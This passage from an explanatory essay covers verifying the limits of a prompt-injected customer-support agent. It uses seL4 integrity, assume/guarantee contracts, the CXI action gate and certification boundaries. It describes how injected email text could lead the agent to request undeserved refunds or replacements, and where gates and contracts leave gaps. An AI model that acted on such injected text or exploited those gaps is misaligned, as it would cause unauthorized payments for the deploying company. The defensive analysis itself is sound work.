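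Even with all these conditions met, one component can mislead another. In the network device, a controller program asks a small trusted program, the router manager, to switch networks. The controller has Send authority over the channel between them, and the definition of integrity allows a component with this authority to write any message into the registers of a waiting receiver. If an attacker tricked the controller into asking for the wrong network, the kernel would correctly deliver the request, and the manager would make the switch using its own access to both networks. Because the manager has so much authority, the theorems do not cover the steps it takes, and someone must verify its code separately.

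The support agent and the dispatcher would be in the same position on seL4. The kernel could guarantee that the agent never writes to the payment ledger, but it would still deliver a record requesting an undeserved refund. The integrity theorem attributes each change to the component running at the time, so it would attribute the payment to the dispatcher. A project report by Trustworthy Systems, the group behind seL4, accordingly lists component isolation, the research area that includes the integrity theorem, separately from the correctness of trusted components.

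### Contracts for the agent and the dispatcher

A pair of contracts can supply the missing limit on the dispatcher. *Symbolic Temporal Supervision of LLM Agents Using Contracts* (2026) defines a contract as a triple (V, A, G), where V is the set of variables involved, A is what a component assumes about its surroundings, and G is what it guarantees if A holds. In one example, an agent guarantees that it will issue refunds only within an authorized limit, assuming that a policy service supplies valid information about that limit. The paper's contracts cover the agent's tool calls, so limiting what happens after a call requires a second contract for the program that reads the output.

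For the support example, the two contracts could be:

| Component | Assumes | Guarantees |
|---|---|---|
| Agent with its harness | Nothing about the emails or the model's behavior | Every record it appends is valid, with one of the 10,000 order numbers and one of the five routes |
| Dispatcher | Every record in the queue is valid, and no other program changes its history of refunds | For any sequence of records, it refunds at most $200 in total on each order, makes at most 50 refunds a day and makes no other payments |

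The harness can fulfil the agent's contract by rejecting every invalid record, whatever the model writes. The dispatcher's contract is harder to prove because it must hold for every sequence of valid records an attacker could choose.

The bound then follows in five steps:

1. Only the agent's harness can write to the queue, so every record in it is valid.
2. No other program changes the refund history, so the dispatcher's assumptions hold and its guarantee applies.
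3. With at most 50 refunds a day and $200 per order, the dispatcher pays at most $10,000 a day.
4. Across all 10,000 orders, it pays at most $2,000,000.
5. The dispatcher is the only program that acts on the records, so the agent can cause no other payments through the queue.

After D days, the loss is therefore at most:

min($10,000 × D, $2,000,000)

An attack that went unnoticed for 30 days could cost up to $300,000. The engineer got the same daily and total figures by reading the dispatcher's code, but the contracts show which fact each step depends on. The company can replace the model without a new proof, and if it rewrites the dispatcher, it has to re-prove only the dispatcher's contract.

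### A program that nobody modeled

Suppose another team writes a program that reads the same queue every night. For each `replace` record, the program gives the customer $50 in store credit as an apology. The team has permission to read the queue and does not mention the program to the engineers who wrote the contracts.

Steps 1 to 4 still hold, because every record is valid and the dispatcher stays within its limits, so the agent and the dispatcher both meet their contracts. Step 5 fails because the dispatcher is no longer the only program that acts on the records. If injected text leads the agent to append 1,000 `replace` records in a day, the new program gives away $50,000, five times the daily limit that the company thought it had proved. If the program also accepts repeated records for the same order, the total loss has no limit.

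A different addition would break step 2. Suppose the new program also deletes old entries from the dispatcher's refund history to save space. The dispatcher could then refund an order that had already reached $200. Ciliberto and colleagues give a general condition for combining components without losing what someone has proved about each. If E(U) stands for the effects that U's description allows, and U ⊗ V for the two components running together, the condition is:

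E(U ⊗ V) ⟹ E(U) ∧ E(V)

A combination passes the test only if each component's own description already allows everything that happens when both run. This combination fails because the dispatcher's description does not allow its history to shrink. However, engineers can test only the combinations they know about.

The company can protect step 5 by letting only the dispatcher read the queue. On seL4, authority confinement, which is proved for the kernel, would then prevent the components it covers from acquiring the right to receive records. The dispatcher's contract would limit what the dispatcher does with the records. If the dispatcher forwards them to other programs, its contract must also cover those programs' effects.

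### Context-to-Execution Integrity

Other designs run the check just before an action takes effect. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) presents one such system, CXI, which is meant to prevent "authority laundering", in which text that should serve only as evidence is used to choose, approve or trigger an action. For example, a build log may identify the file that failed, but it should not determine which tool runs or mark a change as approved.

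CXI's gate puts each proposed action into a fixed form called a manifest, m. Santos-Grueiro states the guarantee as:

Admit(m) ⇒ Fields(m) ∧ Effects(m) ∧ Invoke(m)

If the gate admits an action, all three conditions hold for the same manifest:

- Fields: each field that selects or authorizes the action, such as the tool or the recipient, gets its value from a trusted source or from a typed release, which is an endorsement for one field only. After trusted code validates a file path from a log, the path can fill the field for the file, but it cannot choose the tool.
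- Effects: if the action includes something that the receiving tool interprets, such as a code patch or a database command, trusted code has authorized its exact effect in the current state. The same patch needs new authorization if the underlying code has changed.
- Invoke: a one-time permit allows this particular call. Injected text therefore can't make the agent repeat a legitimate action without a new permit.

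Any later change to the action no longer matches the manifest, and the gate refuses to run it.

In 400 test episodes with coding agents, no action got past the gate without the required authority, and the agents completed 231 tasks safely. Of the other 169 episodes, 73 produced output that the system could not parse, 61 had no authorization for the effect, and 35 ran an authorized action but did not complete the task. In a separate set of 20 attack cases, a simplified provenance check on arguments stopped 12, and the full system stopped all 20. The simplified check missed attacks that targeted the decision to make a call.

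These results show that the gate enforces its policy, but they would not reveal a mistake in the policy. People had to classify 149 fields for the 24 tools and other endpoints tested. An audit of the policies recorded 18 problems, half of them high-severity. The problems included missing protection for data that could change a program's behavior and for text that other programs might later act on.

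CXI's guarantee ends when the action takes effect. An agent may copy untrusted text into a comment or report, where the text has no authority. If another program that can cause effects later reads the text, that program must treat it as untrusted again. A program without its own gate might not. The guarantee also does not cover effects that bypass the gate.

For the support queue, whoever writes the CXI policy would have to decide how to classify the route. Appending a record looks harmless, and nothing in the record's format shows that the word `refund` leads to a payment, so the policy writer needs to know what the dispatcher does with the route to protect it. The gate would then reject a `refund` route based on a customer's email unless trusted code had approved it, perhaps after checking the carrier's delivery record. The policy writer would also have to protect `replace` once the apology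 program began to read the queue.

### Where to draw the boundary

The company could certify the agent alone, the agent and the software that directly uses its output, or the whole deployment. This choice determines what the certificate covers and which software changes can invalidate it. As Miller and Shapiro pointed out, it does not change the agent's authority.

| Boundary | What the company can claim | What it must check again after a change |
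|---|---|---|
| Agent alone | The agent appends only valid records | The harness and the record format |
| Agent and dispatcher | Through the dispatcher, the agent can cause at most $10,000 in payments a day and $2,000,000 in total | The harness, the record format, the dispatcher, the number of orders and who can read or write the queue and the refund history |
| Whole deployment | The agent's output can cause at most a stated loss through any program | Every program, shared store and outside service that the output can reach |

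The certificate for the agent alone is the easiest to maintain. It remains true when another team adds a program that reads the queue, because it does not cover payments. For the same reason, it is little help to someone who needs to know how much money the company could lose.

Including the dispatcher in the certification produces a figure in dollars. The daily limit stays the same as the business grows, but each new order adds $200 to the total. The company must also control who can read the queue, or disclose that the figure covers only payments the dispatcher makes.

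A certificate for the whole deployment would be the most useful and the hardest to keep valid. If the company runs 40 programs and releases a new version of each every two weeks, any of 40 × 26 = 1,040 releases a year might invalidate the certificate. The harness and the dispatcher account for only 52 of them. Ciliberto and colleagues' method can reduce the work by letting a new system reuse the proof for a payment module if the module's code and operating conditions are the same. Someone still has to check those conditions and any new combination of components. How restrictions can keep their meaning as an agent's workflow changes is still a central open question, according to the survey *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026).

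For a system like the support queue, the boundary around the agent and the dispatcher is probably the best compromise, because the company can restrict the queue to one reader and enforce the limits in one program. This boundary works less well when output goes into storage that many programs share. A certificate for Cline's triage agent and its direct consumers would have helped only if someone had counted the nightly release workflow among them. A certificate for the whole deployment would also have depended on GitHub's rule for discarding cache entries. GitHub had changed that rule shortly before Cline set up the agent, and a similar change afterward could have invalidated the certificate without any change to Cline's software.
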